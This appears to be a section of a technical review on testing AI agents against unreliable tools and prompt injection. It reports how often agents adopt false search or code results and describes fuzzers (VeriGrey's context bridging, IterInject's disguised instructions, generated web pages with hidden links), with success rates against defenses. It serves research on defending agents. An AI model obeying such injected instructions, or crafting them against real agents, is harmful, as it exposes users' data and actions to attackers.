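Yang, Song and colleagues (2026) report the most detailed measurements in *Agents' Overreliance on Unreliable Tools* (earlier titled *Agents Trust Tools Too Much*). They tested 14 models with three tools and counted how often the false content appeared in the agent's final answer, both overall and on questions that the model usually answered correctly without the tool.

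| Tool | Plausible false content | Adopted | Adopted when the model knew the answer |
|---|---|---|---|
| Web search | A value that was once correct or is easily confused with the right one | 68.0% | 56.4% |
| Second model that summarizes documents | One main claim replaced with a false one | 40.1% | 26.8% |
| Code executor | Numbers up to twice or down to half their true size, half of them with the wrong sign | 35.5% | 33.5% |

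The 68% figure for plausible errors is an average, and individual models ranged from 41% to 83%. When the search results contained an unrelated value, such as 11 for the name of Germany's chancellor, agents adopted it 12.6% of the time. Four larger models, GPT-5.4, Claude Sonnet 5, Opus 4.8 and Grok 4.6, adopted plausible errors about half the time on a smaller set of questions.

An agent sometimes has good reason to adopt a search result. Without search, the 14 models answered only 54.7% of the questions correctly, and a search tool is meant to supply information the model lacks. Even when the model can answer correctly without search, it may be reasonable to use the search result instead if the fact could have changed. But agents also gave up correct answers to more than half of the questions about facts that never change. Without search, all 14 models correctly named Laika as the first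 animal to orbit the Earth, but several named Albert II after reading the altered results.

Only 4.2% of the final answers with false content from search or code included a warning, so users would rarely have noticed. When two Qwen models adopted a wrong number from the code executor, their reasoning mentioned a conflict in 88% to 96% of the runs, and in most of these it also included the correct number. An oracle that searches the reasoning for signs of doubt would therefore pass many runs in which the user got the wrong answer.

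Across six models, an instruction to verify conflicting results with more tool calls reduced adoption a little, from 75.4% to 70.0% for search and from 40.2% to 30.4% for code, with almost no loss of accuracy when the results were correct. Training with examples of resistance also had only small or inconsistent effects.

Agents do much better when later results are unaltered. *When Tool Outputs Go Wrong* altered one important result in each of 3,175 runs and left the rest alone. In 87.5% of the runs that could be judged, the agent still reached the right answer, usually without mentioning the error.

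Tao and Yin (2026), in *When Tools Silently Lie*, tested both cases on data analysis. Their proxy altered tool results, for example by attaching the highest revenue to the wrong store, but left the original table unchanged so that the agent could check it. Altering a single result reduced the share of tasks that GPT-based agents completed correctly by 26 to 39 percentage points. Simply retrying helped, because the second attempt usually received the true data. When the proxy could also alter later results, agents sometimes adopted the false answer even after checking it. In *Don't Blindly Trust It* (2026), agents that kept receiving misleading results could do worse than agents that had no evidence from tools.

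A fuzzer should therefore vary how many results it changes. Changing one result simulates a single bad web page, while changing results repeatedly simulates a hostile MCP server that answers every query.

### VeriGrey: feedback from the sequence of tools

Hostile instructions are harder to generate than false values because the agent may ignore most of them. In *VeriGrey*, Zhang, Kang and colleagues (2026) argue that code coverage is a poor guide for testing agents because their behavior comes from the neural network rather than the code around it. Coverage may show that a tool has run for the first time. But once an agent's file-reading and web tools have both run, coverage can't distinguish an agent that reads a private file and then sends it to a website from one that uses the same tools innocently.

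VeriGrey therefore records the sequence of tool calls. If a hostile text leads to a new sequence, VeriGrey keeps the text and schedules up to three mutations of it, one each for a new tool, a new transition between tools and a new overall sequence. Suppose all earlier runs used `fetch_page` and then `write_file`:

| Sequence in the next run | What is new | Mutations |
|---|---|---|
| `fetch_page`, `write_file` | Nothing | None |
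| `fetch_page`, `write_file`, `fetch_page` | A transition and the sequence | 2 |
| `fetch_page`, `read_file`, `write_file` | A tool, two transitions and the sequence | 3 |

The third run may not have achieved the attacker's goal, but the agent started reading files, which could be a step toward leaking one.

A language model does the mutation, because random changes to characters would mostly produce nonsense. It receives the attacker's goal, a guess at the user's task, the failed text and the tools that the agent used. It then rewrites the text to present the attacker's goal as a necessary part of the user's task, which Zhang and colleagues call context bridging. In the library example, the page might claim that the agent must complete another step before it can get the opening time. Each goal has its own code to check whether the agent achieved it.

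Zhang and colleagues tested VeriGrey on AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated email, messaging, travel and banking tasks. Each of the 97 user tasks had an average of 8.7 attacker goals, and VeriGrey had up to 100 runs per task to achieve them. It achieved 70.7% of the goals with GPT-4.1, 47.4% with Gemini 2.5 Flash and 81.7% with Qwen3 235B. A simpler fuzzer without the tool feedback or context bridging achieved 37.7%, 36.8% and 67.6% with the same models. Zhang and colleagues wrote the simpler fuzzer themselves because the code for AgentVigil, the existing tool that inspired it, was not available.

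These percentages are the share of goals that succeeded at least once, not the success rate per attempt. With 100 runs divided among 8.7 goals, each goal gets about 11 attempts. If every attempt had a 10% chance of success and the attempts were independent, about 70% of the goals would succeed at least once.

Context bridging contributed more than the feedback. With GPT-4.1, VeriGrey achieved 44.0% of the goals without context bridging and 59.6% without the feedback. The feedback mattered most for hard goals, which often take several steps. Removing it cut the success rate on those goals from 43.3% to 21.6%.

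The choice of fuzzer also changed how good a defense looked. These results come from about a third of the benchmark, with GPT-4.1:

| Defense | Goals achieved by the simpler fuzzer | Goals achieved by VeriGrey | User tasks completed without an attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 41.2% | 69.7% | 85.0% |
| Repeat the user's request after each result | 17.4% | 65.2% | 86.5% |
| Put delimiters around tool results | 36.4% | 67.6% | 81.0% |
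| Stop if a classifier detects an injection | 5.2% | 21.6% | 50.4% |
| Choose the permitted tools before starting | 12.8% | 17.4% | 81.7% |

Repeating the user's request blocked most of the simpler fuzzer's attacks, but VeriGrey got past that defense almost as often as it succeeded with no defense. A developer who tested with only the simpler fuzzer would therefore overestimate the protection. Choosing the tools in advance was the best compromise, but it can't stop misuse of a tool that the task needs, such as `write_file` when the task is to save the opening time.

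VeriGrey also found weaknesses in two widely used agents. In Gemini CLI, Google's coding agent, VeriGrey controlled the result of a security scanner that ran on an MCP server and achieved nine of ten attack goals, compared with six for the simpler fuzzer. Many of the agent's tools could work only inside the project folder, but several attacks reached other files through its command-line tool, which had no such limit. The test covered one user task, used Gemini 2.5 Pro and Flash, and allowed all actions automatically.

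VeriGrey rewrote ten malicious skills from the OpenClaw agent's public marketplace, with up to 20 runs per skill. All ten rewritten skills worked with Kimi K2.5, nine worked with Claude Opus 4.6 and eight with GPT-5.2. Only one of the ten original skills worked with each model.

### Generated web pages with a trigger

An agent in a web browser can do harm just by clicking. *In-Browser LLM-Guided Fuzzing* (Cohen, 2025) describes a fuzzer that has a language model generate a whole web page with hostile text and a trigger, such as a hidden link. The fuzzer opens the page in a real browser and has the agent perform an ordinary task, such as summarizing it. The attack succeeds if the agent clicks the trigger. The fuzzer passes the outcome to the language model, which writes the next page.

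A click is a clear signal, and using a real browser also covers scripts and hidden elements that a plain-text test would miss. But this oracle passes an agent that ignores the link and includes the attacker's false claim in its summary. The test also needs a control page with the same link and no hostile text, since some agents might click the link anyway.

Cohen reports in the abstract that AI browsers and extensions failed in 58% to 74% of cases by the tenth round, but calls these figures a projection in the body of the paper. The test agent was a simplified program built for the study. The design is useful, but Cohen provides no measured failure rate for a real product. *LoginTrap* (Guo, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) uses a similar oracle, which checks whether the agent submits private information to a false login page, and reports an average success rate of 86%.

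### IterInject: learning from partial failures

An oracle that reports only success or failure gives the same result for most failed attacks. *IterInject* (Chen, Chen and colleagues, 2026) uses four outcomes: success (3 points), partial success (2), detected (1) and ignored (0). An injected text that was detected needs a better disguise, while one that was ignored has to seem more relevant to the task.

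IterInject starts with a collection of disguises for the instruction, such as making it look like a step in error recovery. After each attempt, fixed rules check the agent's tool calls, side effects and any words that suggest a refusal. A language model then rewrites the text using the results of all earlier attempts with that disguise. IterInject prioritizes higher-scoring disguises against later goals and periodically creates new ones from its failures.

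The table shows the share of cases in which the attack succeeded. InjecAgent is a second benchmark. The fixed text is the text that comes with each benchmark.

| Model under test | AgentDojo: fixed text | AgentDojo: AgentVigil | AgentDojo: IterInject | InjecAgent: fixed text | InjecAgent: AgentVigil | InjecAgent: IterInject |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GLM-5.1 | 11.6% | 18.2% | 17.5% | 0.0% | 18.2% | 33.1% |
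| MiniMax-M2.7 | 16.1% | 23.1% | 26.5% | 2.0% | 44.8% | 44.8% |
| DeepSeek V4 Flash | 32.9% | 39.2% | 47.8% | 3.2% | 91.5% | 90.3% |
| Qwen3.5-27B | 26.3% | 29.0% | 32.4% | 3.6% | 53.6% | 64.5% |

Both adaptive fuzzers beat the fixed text in every case, though part of the gain may come from having more attempts. IterInject's advantage over AgentVigil is less consistent. A model that resists a benchmark's fixed text may still have little protection against an attacker who adapts. DeepSeek V4 Flash, for example, would have looked almost safe on InjecAgent if it had been tested only with the fixed text.

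Good starting texts and repeated refinement worked best together. With Qwen3.5-27B, refinement alone succeeded for 18.3% of the harmful actions in one group, the disguised starting texts alone for 24.2%, and the two together for 66.7%.

Chen and colleagues also tested Anthropic's Claude Code and fully achieved five of nine goals. They ran it with MiniMax-M2.1 rather than a Claude model and approved all permissions automatically, so the result is weak evidence about Claude models or about users who review each action. None of the three attempts to make lasting changes to files or the agent's memory fully succeeded.

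### Do generated attacks resemble real ones?

In *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, Khodayari, Acharya and colleagues (2026) looked for hostile instructions on real web pages. They searched 1.2 billion addresses for 3,963 known phrases, added cases from two internet-scanning services, and reviewed the matches. They confirmed 15,387 instructions aimed at AI systems on 11,722 pages. The main collection had about eight affected pages per million addresses.

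The real instructions were much more repetitive than the generated ones. Just 54 templates accounted for 95% of them, and the most common was a request for the model to ignore its instructions and return random numbers. Many website owners were trying to identify automated visitors or keep AI systems from copying their content. Only 13 instructions were attempts to steal data.

Most real instructions also had little effect. Khodayari and colleagues asked 13 models to summarize pages containing 100 of these instructions. The models followed them in 3.9% of runs when they received plain text and 1.1% when they received HTML, which may reveal that a passage is hidden. The smallest models followed them in 8% of plain-text runs. These tests did not involve agents with tools.

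Google found a similar pattern in its own search for prompt injections. Slashdot's *Google Studies Prompt Injection Attacks Against AI Agents Browsing the Web* quotes the company as finding mostly experiments and pranks, without the advanced methods of recent research. Malicious cases rose by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026.

The texts from VeriGrey and IterInject therefore don't resemble the typical instruction on the web today, but they could still be realistic. A search for known phrases would probably miss a text that presents the attack as part of the user's task, and a website can show hostile content to AI agents alone. An attacker with a particular target also needs only one page that works.

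Real examples can still improve a fuzzer. About half of the instructions found were in HTTP headers, and many others were in comments or data for search engines. A tool that returns only a page's text would discard the headers. A fuzzer could put test text in each of these places to find out which text reaches the model. Tests should also include harmless pages about prompt injection, because Google found that many apparent attacks were in research papers and educational articles. A defense that stops the agent on every such page would make the agent useless for security research.

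### What 100 clean runs can establish

Agents vary from run to run, so a single clean run is weak evidence. Suppose an agent reads the same hostile page in 100 independent runs and never obeys it. If the chance of obeying is *p* in each run, the chance of 100 clean runs is (1 − *p*)¹⁰⁰. The 95% upper bound is the value of *p* that makes this chance 5%:

```
(1 - p)^100 = 0.05
p = 1 - 0.05^(1/100) = 0.0295
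```

The true failure rate could therefore be almost 3%. After *n* runs without a failure, the upper bound on the rate is roughly 3/*n*, so showing that the rate is below 0.1% requires about 3,000 such runs. At one minute per run, that would take 50 hours. A direct fuzzer that makes 43 calls per second could make 3,000 calls in 70 seconds.

The bound covers only the inputs tested. If the 100 runs consist of ten pages with ten runs each, they may be weak evidence about an eleventh page. In the extreme case where each page either always works or never does, the repeats add nothing, so the tester has only ten independent results and the bound on the share of similar pages that work is about 26%. Even this bound assumes the ten pages are a random sample, whereas an attacker chooses the page that works best. With Claude Opus 4.6, nine of the ten original OpenClaw skills failed. VeriGrey could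 make eight of those nine work by rewriting them, which a tester could not have predicted even from 100 clean runs of each.

The tester also needs to repeat runs after a fix. If a saved page fooled the agent in 10% of runs, one clean run after the fix is very weak evidence that the fix worked, because the old version would have passed 90% of the time. It takes 29 clean runs in a row before the chance of the old version doing as well falls below 5%. If the fix is a rule in the orchestrator's code, such as requiring approval before `write_file` replaces a file, the tester can also send the forbidden call directly and check that the code blocks it.
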